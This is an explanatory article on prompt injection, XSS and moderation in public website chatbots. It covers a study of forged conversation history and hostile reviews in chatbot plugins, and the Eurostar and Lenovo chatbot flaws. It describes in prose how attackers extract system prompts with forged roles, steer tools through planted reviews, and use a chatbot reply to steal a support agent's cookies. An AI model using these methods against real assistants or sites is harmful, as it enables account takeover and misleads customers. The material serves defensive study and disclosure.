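# Public chat assistants that take questions from strangers and publish text: prompt injection, sanitisation and moderation

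## How a stranger's question reaches a model and a web page

A public chat assistant is a part of a website where any visitor can type a question and a large language model (LLM) writes the reply. An LLM is a program that continues a text by predicting, one fragment at a time, what is likely to come next. Shops, government offices and software projects use these assistants in place of a help desk or a list of frequently asked questions. Many sites keep a log of the exchanges for their staff, and some put the question and answer on a public page, where search engines and other language models find them.

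The visitor's question is untrusted text, meaning text whose author the site does not control. Product reviews, form entries and bug report titles are also untrusted. Such text caused problems on the web long before language models, usually because a program treated someone's content as a command. A chat assistant passes the question through several programs in a row (a database, a model, a browser, perhaps a second model), and each either has its own way of telling commands from content or has no way to do so.

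Suppose a town library runs an assistant for people learning to use computers, and a visitor types "What does the `<b>` tag do?" In HTML, the language of web pages, `<b>` is a command that switches on bold type. If the software handles this harmless question carelessly, the visitor's browser can follow the command instead of displaying it as text.

### The form and the database

The visitor's browser sends the question to the library's server, which saves it in a database. Many databases use a command language called SQL. If a careless developer writes code that pastes the visitor's words directly into an SQL command, someone who types the right punctuation can end that command and add another that copies or deletes the library's records. This attack is called SQL injection.

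Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection. The developer writes the command with a placeholder, such as `INSERT INTO questions (text) VALUES (?)`, and the server sends the visitor's words to the database separately. The database interprets the command before filling in the placeholder, so the visitor's words can't change what the command does. A 2024 alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA and the FBI, *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems*, recommends this method over removing suspicious characters from the input, which is brittle and often bypassed. MySQL has supported parameterised queries since 2004, but the agencies still needed to recommend them twenty years later because attackers had used SQL injection against a file-transfer product, affecting thousands of organisations.

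### The model

The server next assembles a prompt, the full text that the model will continue. It begins with the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, such as "Help beginners with computers, and keep answers under a hundred words." The visitor's question follows. Each piece has a message role, a label for where the text comes from. The library's instructions are labelled "system", the question about `<b>` is labelled "user", earlier replies are labelled "assistant", and the results of searches or other programs are labelled "tool". The names vary a little. OpenAI's published format for its gpt-oss models puts what most people mean by the system prompt under "developer" and uses "system" for settings such as the model's knowledge cutoff.

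The application sets these labels, so a visitor cannot become the developer merely by claiming to be one. The labels also affect which instructions the model follows. OpenAI's *Our approach to the Model Spec* describes giving each instruction a level of authority and telling the model to favour the higher level when two conflict. But labels don't reliably show who wrote the text. OpenAI (2024) defined the "user" role to cover both what end users type and any other data the developer wants to supply, so a stranger's product review could arrive under the same label as the customer's question.

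Prompt injection is text that makes a language model follow the text author's instructions instead of the developer's or user's. In direct injection, the author is the person using the assistant. For example, a visitor tells the library's assistant to forget about computers and write an advertisement for a casino. In indirect injection, the author plants the text in material that the assistant reads later, usually while serving someone else. For example, a job applicant hides a line in a CV instructing the recruiter's screening model to approve the candidate.

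Prompt injection plainly resembles SQL injection, and the resemblance misleads people. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argued that web developers who treat the two alike will trust defences that do not hold. A database has a stage at which it determines what the command is, but a model has no such stage. The model receives everything in the prompt, including labels, as a single sequence of tokens (fragments of text) and runs the same calculation over all of them to predict the next one. Developers therefore have no placeholder where they could put the visitor's words so that they count only as data.

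A developer wouldn't want the assistant to ignore every instruction in untrusted text. If the library's visitor adds "in one sentence, please", the assistant should comply. The library needs to separate the requests a visitor may make from those a visitor may not, and a rule about punctuation can't do this because it requires judging what the request means.

Developers can train models to rank instructions, mark the untrusted parts of a prompt, or filter for known attacks. David C regards all of these as attempts to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that has none. He considers them worth using because they make attacks less likely to succeed, but they can't guarantee safety. He prefers to treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In security jargon, a confused deputy is a component that someone tricks into using privileges they lack on their behalf.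 His practical rule, drawn from an exchange between the programmers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model handling text from some party should have no more privileges than that party. An assistant that answers anonymous visitors should therefore have no access to the library's membership records, even if its system prompt forbids it to discuss them.

Two weeks later OpenAI came to much the same view in *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025), a post about a browser in which ChatGPT can click and type for its user. The company had trained a model to invent attacks on the browser. In one, the attacking model planted an email in a test inbox. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the assistant found the email and sent the user's resignation to the chief executive instead. OpenAI retrained the assistant against such attacks, but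 wrote that prompt injection, like scams aimed at people, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". This admission deserves weight because it goes against the company's commercial interest. OpenAI's optimism that fast patches will reduce the risk is harder to assess, because the post gives no success rates for attacks before or after the retraining.

### The visitor's browser

The model outputs "The `<b>` tag makes text bold." Replies usually contain markup, the HTML or Markdown codes that a browser or other renderer turns into formatting, links, images or scripts. In Markdown, two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold. The site converts the Markdown to HTML, and the browser displays it.

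If the library's site puts the visitor's question into the page unchanged, the browser acts on `<b>` instead of displaying it, and the visitor sees "What does the tag do?" with the last words in bold. That is only confusing, but HTML also has elements that run programs, and a page that lets `<b>` through will probably let those through too. Attackers can exploit this through cross-site scripting (XSS), in which a site shows an attacker's text as code and another person's browser runs it. For instance, a script in a book review could change the email address on the account of each logged-in member who opens the page. The *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a non-profit that writes security guidance for developers, lists impersonation and the theft of sensitive data among the results.

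The basic defence is escaping, which converts special characters so that a browser displays them as text instead of acting on them. The site sends `&lt;b&gt;`, and the visitor sees `<b>`. The right conversion depends on where the text will appear, because browsers apply different rules to the body of a page, a web address and a script. Developers cannot tell where text will end up when they filter it on arrival, so OWASP advises them to escape it close to the point of display.

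Escaping everything would also disable the formatting that the library wants in its answers. Sanitising software instead parses the markup and removes any element or attribute that is not on an approved list, so it can remove a script element but keep bold type and paragraphs. A later step that alters the text can undo this, so a site that turns Markdown into HTML has to sanitise the resulting HTML. Sanitising programs need regular updates because attackers keep finding ways past them.

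A content security policy (CSP) backs up both. It is a list, sent with a web page, of the sources from which the browser may load scripts, images and frames. If the library's policy lists only its own server, the browser will refuse a script from anywhere else. OWASP treats a CSP as a second layer of defence because developers easily get the list wrong.

All this applies to the model's reply as much as to the visitor's question. The reply in the library's case contains `<b>` for a good reason, but a visitor could just as easily ask for harmful markup. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* recommends treating the model as any other user. If a developer escapes what visitors type but trusts what the assistant writes, a visitor can get around the escaping by asking the assistant to write the markup.

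### The staff log

Visitors who attack only the page in front of them affect only themselves, unless the site saves the text. In stored XSS, the site stores the attacker's code, which runs each time someone opens the page or log that displays it. MITRE, a US non-profit that catalogues attack methods, traces the flaw to an application that accepts the script as valid input and later fails to encode it.

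A chat log is a good target for attackers because the people who open it have power over the site. GeekyBot, a chatbot plugin for the website software WordPress, let a visitor without an account put a script in a chat message, and the script ran whenever an administrator opened the Chat History page, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2025-15266* (2026), an entry in the Spanish cybersecurity institute's catalogue. The entry rates the flaw's severity at 7.2 out of 10 and lists versions up to 1.1.7 as affected. WPScan's *GeekyBot* (2026) extends the range to 1.1.8 and lists 1.1.9 as the repaired version, so a site owner who relied on INCIBE's range and updated only to 1.1.8 would have stayed exposed.

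The script stays in the log whether the language model refuses the message or answers it sensibly. A flaw in another WordPress chatbot, WPBot, let attackers bypass the model altogether and submit a conversation that had never taken place. *CVE-2026-13731 Detail* (2026), from the US government's vulnerability database, NVD, traces the flaw to the request that saves a conversation. WPBot checked that request against a code, but printed the code on every public page of the site, where any anonymous visitor could copy it.

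### The public page and its later readers

The library publishes the question about `<b>` and its answer on a page for beginners. The same scripting flaw can now affect people who never used the assistant. Simple Ajax Chat, a public chat box for WordPress with no language model, had a flaw of this kind. WPScan's *Simple Ajax Chat < 20260827* (2026) traces it to the step that turns web addresses in messages into links. The flaw let a stranger run scripts in the browser of anyone viewing the chat, including administrators.

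A public page can also fail when every character is correctly escaped. Suppose the submission had been a question about renewing a library card, and the answer gave a swindler's telephone number as the library's help line. A reader would see the number under the library's name and ring it. Only a person or program that checks what the text claims can catch this. The simplest arrangement is pre-moderation, which means holding a submission until a reviewer approves it for publication. For example, a librarian might read the week's questions every Friday, before any of them appear.

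Search engines then copy the page into their indexes, and may show a line of it beneath the library's address to people who never visit the site. Language models also fetch the page to answer someone's question or summarise it. The stranger's text then enters a new prompt, written by a different developer and serving a different user, and any instructions in it become indirect injection. OpenAI lists forums, social media posts and arbitrary web pages among the places where its browsing assistant may encounter hostile instructions. Escaping the text doesn't protect against this attack, because the attack consists of ordinary sentences.

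If the library's own assistant consults the beginners' page when answering new questions, one bad submission can affect every visitor who asks about the same subject. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security company's reading of OWASP's latest list of risks, says that an injection saved in a model's memory or reference collection remains after the session ends.

### Three harms

Three things have gone wrong along this path: someone has steered the model, a browser has run a stranger's code, and a trusted site has published bad content. Sites often protect against one and assume they have covered the others. Escaping and sanitising reliably stop a stranger's code from running in the browser when developers apply them everywhere. They don't stop anyone from steering the model, because it will follow an escaped instruction as readily as any other. The dependable defence against steering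 is to limit what the model can access and do. Those limits don't keep bad content off the site, since a model with no privileges can still write or repeat a scammer's phone number.

How often each harm occurs is hard to say. Practitioners again put prompt injection first in the list that OWASP (2026) published in August. Invicti reports that OWASP also gathered 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases for that edition. Based on those incidents alone, prompt injection would have missed the top ten. *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Infosecurity Magazine, 2026) relays OWASP's explanation that teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach the databases. That may be right, but the count cannot confirm it, because the record would look the same if attacks were rare. The databases probably also favour flaws in a specific product, such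 as a plugin that runs a stranger's script, because these have a version number and a fix. If someone talks a library's assistant into recommending a casino, there is no faulty product to report.

One harm can also lead to another. If an attacker steers the assistant into writing a script and the site saves the reply unescaped, the script can run when a member of staff opens the log. Escaping the reply would prevent this, but the attacker could still steer the assistant into writing a convincing notice about overdue fines, with a payment link.

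## A study of chatbot plugins on more than 10,000 websites

Message roles protect a chatbot only if visitors cannot set them, and many small sites rely on third-party plugins to prevent that. Kaya and colleagues tested 17 chatbot plugins in a study published in November 2025 and accepted for the 2026 IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy. Eight let a visitor send text labelled as the model's own words, and seven of those also accepted text labelled as the developer's. Fifteen had tools that copied customers' reviews into the model's prompt along with the site's own text.

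### The plugins and their sites

A chatbot plugin is a ready-made component that lets a site owner add an assistant without programming. It displays the chat window, stores the owner's settings and passes messages to a model from a company such as OpenAI, Anthropic or Google. Some of the plugins studied run only on WordPress and need the owner's own account with the model company. Others run on any site, and the plugin's maker handles the account. The study numbers the plugins instead of naming them, so site owners cannot tell from it whether their own plugin is affected.

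The researchers searched Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, and found 10,417 sites with one of the plugins in August 2024 and 17,474 in April 2025. Most were obscure, and only 7.5% of the 2024 sites ranked among the million most popular, but their owners included local governments, universities, charities and international airports. The sites covered 93 languages. Not every site had a working chatbot. Automated checks found one on 76% of the sites with the most popular plugin but on only 53% of those with the second most popular, where failures were often due to setup mistakes or the owner running out of credit.

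### How a visitor forges a conversation

A language model keeps no memory between requests. If the library's visitor asks what `<b>` does and then types "And `<i>`?", the model can make sense of the second question only if the application sends the first question and its answer again. Something therefore has to store the conversation between requests. Giovanny, Bayuningtyas and Mukharom (2026), in *Detectable Epistemic Attack Layers*, treat this history as infrastructure that, like any other, an attacker may be able to rewrite. Eight of the plugins stored the history in the visitor's browser.

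With these plugins, the visitor's browser keeps a list of the conversation's messages, each labelled with its role, starting with the assistant's greeting. When the visitor types a question, the browser adds it to the list and sends the list to the plugin's server. The server adds the owner's system prompt and any relevant text from the site, and passes everything to the model. The browser then adds the model's reply to the list and sends the whole list again with the next question. The server does not check that the list matches what the model and the visitor wrote.

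The visitor's own computer sends the list, so a visitor who knows how to edit a web request can change it. This is called history forging. On the library's site, a visitor could insert an assistant message agreeing to write casino advertisements, and the model would continue a conversation in which it appears to have accepted the job. The visitor could also insert a system message that gives the assistant a new role. The model would receive this message alongside the library's real instructions, under the same label, and nothing in the prompt would show which one the library wrote.

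Forging a label also bypasses the models' training to favour system instructions over those of users, because that training works only if the labels are correct. An attacker can change one word in the request, from "user" to "system", to give hostile text the highest priority the site's owner can assign.

The owner would have had trouble noticing the forged messages, because none of the eight plugins showed them in its dashboard. The plugins recorded the original greeting even when the visitor had replaced it, and left out system messages. With three of the plugins, an owner could have found the forgeries in the model company's logs.

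The same mistake occurs outside plugins. Eurostar's assistant left its earlier messages unchecked, and Strands Agents' *Trusted Message History* describes a more serious form of it. Strands Agents is a programming kit for assistants that use tools, such as a program that looks up an order. In its Python version, if the last message in the history is a request to use a tool, the software runs that tool immediately, without consulting the model. Whoever wrote the history therefore chooses both the tool and its input, even if the model resists injection perfectly.

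### Three hundred live chatbots

To test whether forging worked outside the laboratory, the researchers tried it on 300 randomly chosen sites that used the most popular plugin. They tried to extract the system prompt, which model companies train their models to withhold. As a control, they kept the real greeting and asked for the prompt, and 1% of the chatbots revealed it. They then inserted a forged message presenting the conversation as a debugging session. With this message, 56% of the chatbots revealed the prompt when it had the system role and 55% when it had the assistant role. In total, 219 chatbots (73%) revealed the prompt in at least one of the two forged attempts.

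A model asked for its instructions can invent some, and the researchers had no originals to compare with. They counted a reply as a success if at least three of its sentences looked like a system prompt, with commands in the second person, an assigned role or rules of conduct. Invented instructions could pass that test. But most of the extracted prompts are very unlikely to be invented, because 76% contained more than four-fifths of a template that the plugin's maker supplied or that was available elsewhere, and 31% were exact copies.

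The increase from 1% to 55% overstates the effect of the role. The forged request differed from the control in wording as well as role label, and a visitor could have typed the same debugging story into the chat box. Only the laboratory tests, described below, kept the wording the same.

The extracted prompts mostly contained routine details that owners had added, such as a name for the assistant, an address, facts about the business, or a tone of voice. About 5% included instructions to collect names or contact details, which creates a privacy problem because the plugin's maker and the model company also receive them. About 97% included instructions to turn away questions outside the assistant's subject.

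Owners have a financial reason for that rule, since they pay for every reply. In 2026 Gizmodo reported that people had been getting Pepper, the support chatbot of the restaurant chain Chipotle, to write Python code. One developer, Maksim Soltan, worked out how Pepper's web page communicated with its server, and another, Rob Dezendorf, connected the chatbot to a programming tool. *Demystifying Real-world LLM Service Freeloading* (Hou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) includes the case in a wider survey, which found 513 open-source projects that repackage free access to models, 93% of them created that year. Most of the projects it describes use large free services such as DeepSeek and ChatGPT, which have far more capacity than a small shop's chatbot. The survey therefore shows that people want free model access and know how to automate it, but it provides less evidence of how often they use small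 businesses' chatbots to get it.

### The same attack in different roles

For the controlled tests, the researchers built an imitation shop assistant using 35 product pages from Nalgene, a maker of water bottles. They ran it on 11 models: five from OpenAI (including GPT-4o and o4-mini), three from Anthropic (the newest being Claude Sonnet 4) and three from Google (the strongest being Gemini 2.5 Pro). The models date from 2024 and 2025, and their makers have since released several newer generations, so the exact rates may not apply to an assistant set up today.

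The researchers tested each model with three system prompts. The basic prompt, modelled on a template found on 36% of the live sites, told the assistant to act as a sales agent and set no strict limits. The hardened prompt forbade tasks unrelated to that role, as did a template found on 33% of the sites. The third added an explicit ban on programming. The researchers then sent the same hostile text as a system, assistant or user message, ten times for each combination. The user message represents a plugin that prevents message forging, so an attacker can only type.

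The study tested three attacks: a request for the system prompt, a request for the sales assistant to write a short program, and an attempt to misuse a tool. The table gives the average number of successes in ten runs. Only OpenAI's five models accepted extra system messages, so the rows for the system role leave out the other six models and are not strictly comparable with the rest.

| Attack | Role of the hostile text | Basic prompt | Hardened prompt | Hardened, programming banned |
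|---|---|---|---|---|
| Revealing the system prompt | User | 2.8 | 0 | 0.1 |
| | Assistant | 4.1 | 3.8 | 4.2 |
| | System | 5.4 | 6.0 | 6.0 |
| Writing a program | User | 1.0 | 0 | 0 |
| | Assistant | 5.9 | 3.8 | 1.5 |
| | System | 9.8 | 6.2 | 2.4 |
| Misusing a tool | User | 3.7 | 3.8 | 3.7 |
| | Assistant | 4.8 | 6.7 | 7.1 |
| | System | 3.0 | 4.0 | 6.0 |

When a visitor could only type, the hardened prompt kept the assistant on its subject, and no model wrote the program. With the basic prompt, nearly all the successful attacks were on one model, Gemini 2.0 Flash, which complied every time. When the researchers forged the assistant's earlier messages, the hardened prompt failed in 38% of runs. An explicit ban on programming cut that to 15%, but an owner would have to foresee each kind of unwanted work to ban it.

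According to the study's summary, forging makes attacks three to eight times as successful. The table doesn't give a single multiple, because typed attacks often never succeeded against a hardened prompt. A model with a zero in the table may still be vulnerable. Ten failures in a row are compatible with a true success rate of around a quarter, and the researchers used only one wording for each attack, the best of five they had tried on some of the models. They were measuring the effect of careless plugins, not trying to find the strongest attack.

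### Why hardening did not protect the tools

In the third attack, the assistant had a tool for sending notices on Slack, a workplace messaging service. The owner had instructed it to notify a particular channel whenever a customer mentioned Nalgene or a purchase. The hostile text made it post to a channel read by the whole organisation instead, with the attacker's link in place of the topic. An employee would have seen a suspicious address in a message from the company's own assistant.

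Hardening the system prompt made no difference to a typed attack, which succeeded in about 37% of runs with each of the three prompts. This was because the hardened prompts told the assistant to refuse work outside its role, and sending notices was part of its role. The attacker asked for a permitted action with the wrong destination and contents, which a rule about staying on the subject doesn't forbid. The most popular plugin also keeps its instructions for each tool in a separate block after the main prompt, so an owner can tighten one without changing the other.

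The average again combines two near extremes. Claude 3.5 Haiku and all three Google models misused the tool in every run with a typed attack, while the other seven models hardly ever did. Some of those seven did misuse it when the attack used forged messages. Claude Sonnet 4, for example, resisted the typed attack in all 30 runs but complied with the forged assistant message in all 30.

Hardening the prompt seemed to make attacks with forged assistant messages more successful. GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and Claude 3.5 Sonnet account for the increase. A stricter prompt may make a model more likely to obey anything that looks like an instruction, but a test with one wording and ten runs cannot establish that.

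Few of the live assistants had tools at the time of the study. The most popular plugin introduced them in February 2025, and 144 of its chatbots had a tool enabled by April. The most common were web search, on 43 chatbots, and appointment booking, on 40. Another 42 had custom tools built by their owners for tasks such as tracking orders. The researchers did not test the custom tools because doing so could have changed real records.

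Claude models from Opus 4.8 onwards let a developer add system messages partway through a conversation, according to Anthropic's *Mid-conversation system messages and tool changes*. A later system message takes precedence over the system prompt at the top. Anthropic warns developers not to put outside text in these messages, but a plugin that forwards an unchecked conversation history to one of these models could now pass on a forged system message. The Claude models in the study would have rejected such a message with an error.

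### Customer reviews in the knowledge base

History forging requires a faulty plugin and some technical skill, but the study's other attack requires only a review form. Fifteen of the 17 plugins can scrape text from the owner's site to give the assistant information about the products. Their scrapers remove the HTML and keep all the text a visitor would see, including the reviews on product pages. Without the HTML, nothing separates the shop's description from reviews written by strangers.

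Most of the plugins then use retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). The software divides the collected text into passages and stores them in a searchable knowledge base. When a customer asks about a bottle, it finds the passages closest to the question and adds them to the prompt. A hostile review can therefore enter the prompt each time somebody asks about that product. This is indirect injection, triggered by an innocent customer's question. With all but two of the plugins that had scrapers, owners could not see which passages an answer had drawn on, so an owner who noticed a strange reply would not have known which review to delete.

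The researchers wanted to find out, without planting anything on a real site, how many shops were already exposed. They picked 100 online shops at random from those with a working chatbot built on the most popular plugin. Of these, 41 accepted reviews or comments and 36 displayed them on product pages. The researchers read the reviews on those 36 sites and asked each site's chatbot about one, such as why a named customer had complained about a product. Thirteen chatbots gave details that could only have come from the review.

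The method shows that strangers' words reached the model, but not that the model would have followed an instruction among them. The count of 13 exposed shops is probably low, because the researchers asked each chatbot at most five questions and several chatbots refused to discuss individual customers. A refusal doesn't reveal what is in the knowledge base. With a sample of 100, the true share could plausibly be anywhere from 8% to 21%, and that range applies only to shops using one plugin. The count excludes contact forms, guest articles and support threads, which can carry a stranger's text into the knowledge base in the same way.

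A hostile review also has to be retrieved before it can affect the chatbot's answer. *Can It Reach the Generator?* (Yin, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested seven attacks on a product search system, whereas earlier experiments had given the doctored text directly to the model. When the attacked product had to compete for a place in the results, the first search missed about a fifth of the doctored texts. It missed roughly 40% of those containing crude commands, because the added words made the text a poorer match for the customer's question. These losses suggest that some published success rates are too high. Retrieval protects a shop less when customers ask about a product by name, because an attacker can put the name in the review, as Kaya's team did in its tests.

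### Where the retrieved text goes

A plugin must assign a role to the passages it retrieves. The tool role is meant for such material, and models treat it with the least trust, but only one of the 15 plugins used it. Seven used the system role, which gave a customer's review the same standing as the owner's instructions. Four used the assistant role and three the user role. For the WordPress plugins, the researchers read the roles directly in OpenAI's logs. For most of the others, they had to get the chatbot to report the role itself, and they took the majority answer over five products. This evidence is weaker, although it was correct where they could check it.

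They then tested the effect of the placement. A review on the imitation shop's site contained an instruction for the assistant to search the web for a rival brand, Hydro Flask, and show the results. An innocent customer asked about the Nalgene bottle. The attack counted as a success if the assistant ran the search and displayed the links. The researchers also tried wrapping the retrieved passages in tags that marked them as data. With the basic system prompt, the average number of successes in ten runs was as follows:

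| Where the passages went | Without tags | With tags |
|---|---|---|
| Appended to the system prompt | 4.1 | 3.9 |
| Separate system message (OpenAI models only) | 3.8 | 0.8 |
| User message | 3.1 | 2.4 |
| Assistant message | 1.5 | 1.8 |
| Tool message | 1.3 | 0.9 |

The tool role gave the best protection, far better than the role most plugins used. Hardening the system prompt helped somewhat in most positions, but there were exceptions. When the passages arrived as a user message, GPT-4o ignored the review in every run under the basic prompt but followed it in nine runs out of ten under the hardened one. Tags helped OpenAI's models most, but with Google's models they doubled the attack's success rate in the assistant role, from 30% to 60%.

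When the review was at the end of the system prompt, the more capable models followed it more often. Claude Sonnet 4 did so in nine runs out of ten, and o4-mini and Gemini 2.5 Pro did in all ten, while the older or smaller GPT-4o mini, Claude 3.5 Haiku and Gemini 2.0 Flash never did. The researchers attribute this to the stronger models being better at following whatever the system prompt contains. If they are right, upgrading the model behind a badly built plugin may increase the risk.

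Model companies have since moved towards similar advice. Anthropic's *Mitigate jailbreaks and prompt injections* tells developers to put outside content only in tool results, never in system prompts or ordinary user text. It also recommends encoding that content as JSON, a data format with strict rules for quotation marks, so that no part of a review can appear to be outside it.

Putting text in the tool role makes an injection less likely to succeed, but does not prevent it. Gemini 2.5 Pro still followed the hostile review in six to eight runs out of ten when the text was tagged and in the tool role. Work by Charles Ye, Jasmine Cui and Dylan Hadfield-Menell, which Willison has since highlighted, found that models do not reliably use role labels to distinguish their own privileged text from a user's, and that the style of the text appears to matter too.

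### The remedies and the vendors

History forging is the only problem here with a complete fix. If the plugin's server stores the conversation and accepts only the newest message from the browser, the visitor can't alter earlier messages. Kaya and colleagues suggested that plugin makers could also leave the storage to OpenAI's Threads feature, but Threads belonged to a service that closed in August 2026. OpenAI's *Assistants migration guide* directs developers to that service's replacement, the Responses API, which can also manage conversations.

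A plugin that must keep the chat history in the browser can sign it. The server uses a secret key to compute a code for each real message and sends the code along with the message. When the history comes back, the server recomputes the codes, and any message the visitor forged or altered will not match. The signature should also cover the order of the messages and the conversation they belong to, or a visitor could rearrange real messages or copy them from another chat. Giovanny and colleagues tested checks of this general kind and detected altered history in all 126 cases for each model, with no false alarms. A perfect score is expected because the check compares codes and does not interpret language. For the same reason, it does not protect against a hostile review or an instruction that the visitor openly types.

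Strands Agents likewise advises developers to build the history from their own application's records. For those who cannot, it provides code that strips tool requests from the end of the history. This stops a visitor from running a tool directly, but invented messages elsewhere in the history still reach the model.

To detect reviews, the researchers wrote a program called UGCBuster (UGC stands for user-generated content). It relies on sites usually putting all their reviews in the same part of a page's HTML. It groups the text by its position in the HTML, uses a language model to identify groups with signs of outside authorship, such as usernames and dates, and finds the fewest containers that hold all those groups. The site owner can then exclude those containers from the knowledge base or include them under stricter formatting. On three pages from each of ten shops, UGCBuster found all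 the right containers and wrongly flagged one other, and it cost about five cents a page.

Thirty pages are enough to show that the idea is workable, but nobody was trying to fool the detector, which is also a language model reading strangers' text. Excluding the reviews also has a drawback, since customers may reasonably ask an assistant what other buyers thought. The alternative is to trace how outside text reaches the prompt through the plugin's code, which the researchers thought was too demanding for most plugin makers. This may be getting easier, since CodeQL, GitHub's tool for scanning code, has a query that looks for user-controlled text entering system prompts and tool descriptions.

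For the last remedy, the researchers had a language model rewrite the tool instructions with explicit rules, for example that the assistant must use only the channel and topics the owner had set. Attack success fell by 40 to 75%, a large drop for a few added sentences, but between a quarter and three-fifths of the previously successful attacks still worked. The attacker also had not adapted to the new wording, and the conference's reviewers raised the same concern about the proposed defences in general. A plugin maker could do better by setting the Slack channel in the plugin's code, so that the model cannot choose it. This follows the rule that an assistant serving strangers should have no more privileges than they do, and it works however persuasive the attacker's text is. The contents of the notice would need a similar restriction, with a fixed list of topics instead of free text.

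The researchers reported history forging to the makers of all eight plugins in October 2024, and four replied within three days. By December, the maker of the most popular plugin had moved the history to its server and issued stricter prompt templates, which included a ban on programming. The second most popular plugin remained open to forging. Its maker said that "some plugin workflows rely on the ability to modify messages", and made the plugin log a warning when it detects a forgery. The makers of the other six had not fixed the flaw by the time the study appeared. The seven unfixed plugins were running on about 5,700 sites in April 2025, up from about 3,800 in August 2024.

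The researchers also told the makers of the two most popular plugins about the reviews. Neither took any steps.

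## Chatbot answers that carried working HTML: Eurostar and Lenovo

A visitor who can forge a conversation can largely dictate what the model writes next. This is a bigger problem if the website runs the reply as code, as happened with two companies' public assistants in 2025. On Eurostar's site, a tester got the assistant to put HTML he had chosen into his own chat window. On Lenovo's site, similar HTML also ran for the support agent who took over the conversation.

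### Eurostar's chat window

Eurostar runs high-speed trains between Britain and mainland Europe, and its chatbot answered customers' general questions. Hackread's *Eurostar Accused Researchers of Blackmail for Reporting AI Chatbot Flaws* says the flaws were found by a researcher at Pen Test Partners, a British security firm, who was planning a trip from London. Willing (2025), in *Eurostar’s Chatbot Goes Off the Rails, Security Firm Finds*, quotes at length from the account by Ross Donald, who heads the firm's core testing team and found four flaws.

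The first was a form of history forging. As with the faulty plugins, the visitor's browser sent the whole conversation to the server with each new question. Unlike those plugins, Eurostar's system filtered messages for forbidden content and signed those that passed. But the server verified only the newest message's signature, so Donald could rewrite an earlier message, send a harmless question as the newest one, and have both reach the model. To fix this, Eurostar needed to verify the signature on every message.

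Donald used the altered history to extract the model's name and the system prompt. This did little damage by itself, because the prompt exposed no customer data and some companies, including Anthropic, publish the system prompts of their consumer assistants. But the prompt contained an instruction to write answers in HTML, with links to help articles, which pointed towards the next flaw.

Eurostar's page inserted that HTML without sanitising it. Once Donald could steer the model, he could make it return other HTML in place of the usual link. He used only harmless examples, but an attacker could have inserted a script or a link to a fake payment page in the same way, and either would have appeared inside an official Eurostar answer.

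So far the only person at risk was the one typing. Security researchers call this self-XSS and rate its severity as low. HackerOne, which runs reward schemes for people who report flaws, won't normally accept it unless it affects somebody else's account.

The fourth flaw was in how Eurostar's server handled the identifiers for conversations and messages. Each identifier should have been a UUID, a long value that is very hard to guess, but the server accepted any short piece of text. Donald inferred, but did not test, that this could lead to stored XSS, in which one visitor's hostile reply would load in another visitor's chat. City AM's *Eurostar’s new AI chatbot left customers exposed* reports that Pen Test Partners said it had not tried to open other people's conversations. The attack would work only if Eurostar's server saved conversations under identifiers supplied by the browser and then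 loaded them for a different visitor, and the tests did not show that it did either.

The inference is still reasonable, because the same thing has happened elsewhere. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-51859* (2025) describes a flaw in Chaindesk, a service for building chatbots. An attacker could build a chatbot with a system prompt instructing the model to put a script in its answers, and the script ran for anyone who opened a direct link to the conversation.

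Checking that an identifier looks like a UUID would not be enough to prevent this, since an attacker might have copied a real one. The server should create the identifier itself and check, on every request, that the conversation belongs to the visitor requesting it.

Eurostar told City AM that the chatbot had no access to other systems and that a customer login protected all data. The lack of access is a good defence, since it follows the rule of giving a public assistant no special privileges. The login is a weaker defence against XSS, because a script running in a logged-in customer's browser may be able to act with that customer's access, though nobody showed that a script could do this.

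### The argument over the report

Pen Test Partners emailed its findings on 11 June 2025 to the address Eurostar published for such reports, and wrote again a week later, but got no reply. On 7 July the firm reached Eurostar's head of security through LinkedIn, who told the firm to use the reporting programme, which it had already done. Eurostar had meanwhile handed the programme to an outside contractor and had no record of the email. A Eurostar security executive suggested that the firm's persistence could look like blackmail. Donald replied that blackmail needs a threat and that the firm had made none.

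Eurostar later acknowledged overlooking the email and said it had fixed some of the problems, according to SiliconANGLE's *Researchers say Eurostar accused them of blackmail over AI chatbot flaw disclosure* (2025). Eurostar also told City AM that it had dealt promptly with any issues found in early testing. That is hard to reconcile with overlooking the email, although Donald conceded that Eurostar might have been investigating without telling him. Willing reports that the firm confirmed the fixes before publishing on 22 December, but also quotes Donald as unsure whether Eurostar had fully fixed every flaw.

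### Lenovo's support agents

Lenovo's customer assistant, Lena, ran on OpenAI's GPT-4 and could pass a conversation to a human agent. That handover provided the step missing at Eurostar. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes how the news site's researchers attacked Lena with a single message of about 400 characters.

The researchers began their message with an ordinary question about a laptop's specifications. They then told Lena to answer in several formats, including HTML, in the order that Lenovo's web server expected. Finally, they asked for an image at the end of the answer and stressed that it was important. HTML allows an image to carry a short script that runs if the image fails to load. The researchers gave an address where no image existed, so the script was certain to run. It sent the browser's cookies to a server that they controlled.

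A browser sends a session cookie with each request so that a website recognises someone who has already logged in. Anyone who copies the cookie can often use the account without a password. When the reply first appeared, the script could take only the customer's own cookies. But Lenovo saved the reply in the conversation's history. If the customer then asked for a human agent, the agent's browser loaded the history, failed to find the image and ran the script again, this time with access to the agent's cookies.

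Escaping the customer's message in the agent's window would not have stopped this, because Lena generated the working HTML in its reply. Lenovo's software treated that reply as the company's own text, although a stranger had specified its contents.

Cybernews warns that an attacker could log in as the agent and read other customers' chats, but does not report trying this. That access would be serious on its own. The researchers also thought it might be possible to run system commands and install a backdoor, but said they had not tried to. This is the most speculative possibility, because browsers confine a page's script to what the page can do, and an attacker would need another flaw to take over a computer or server.

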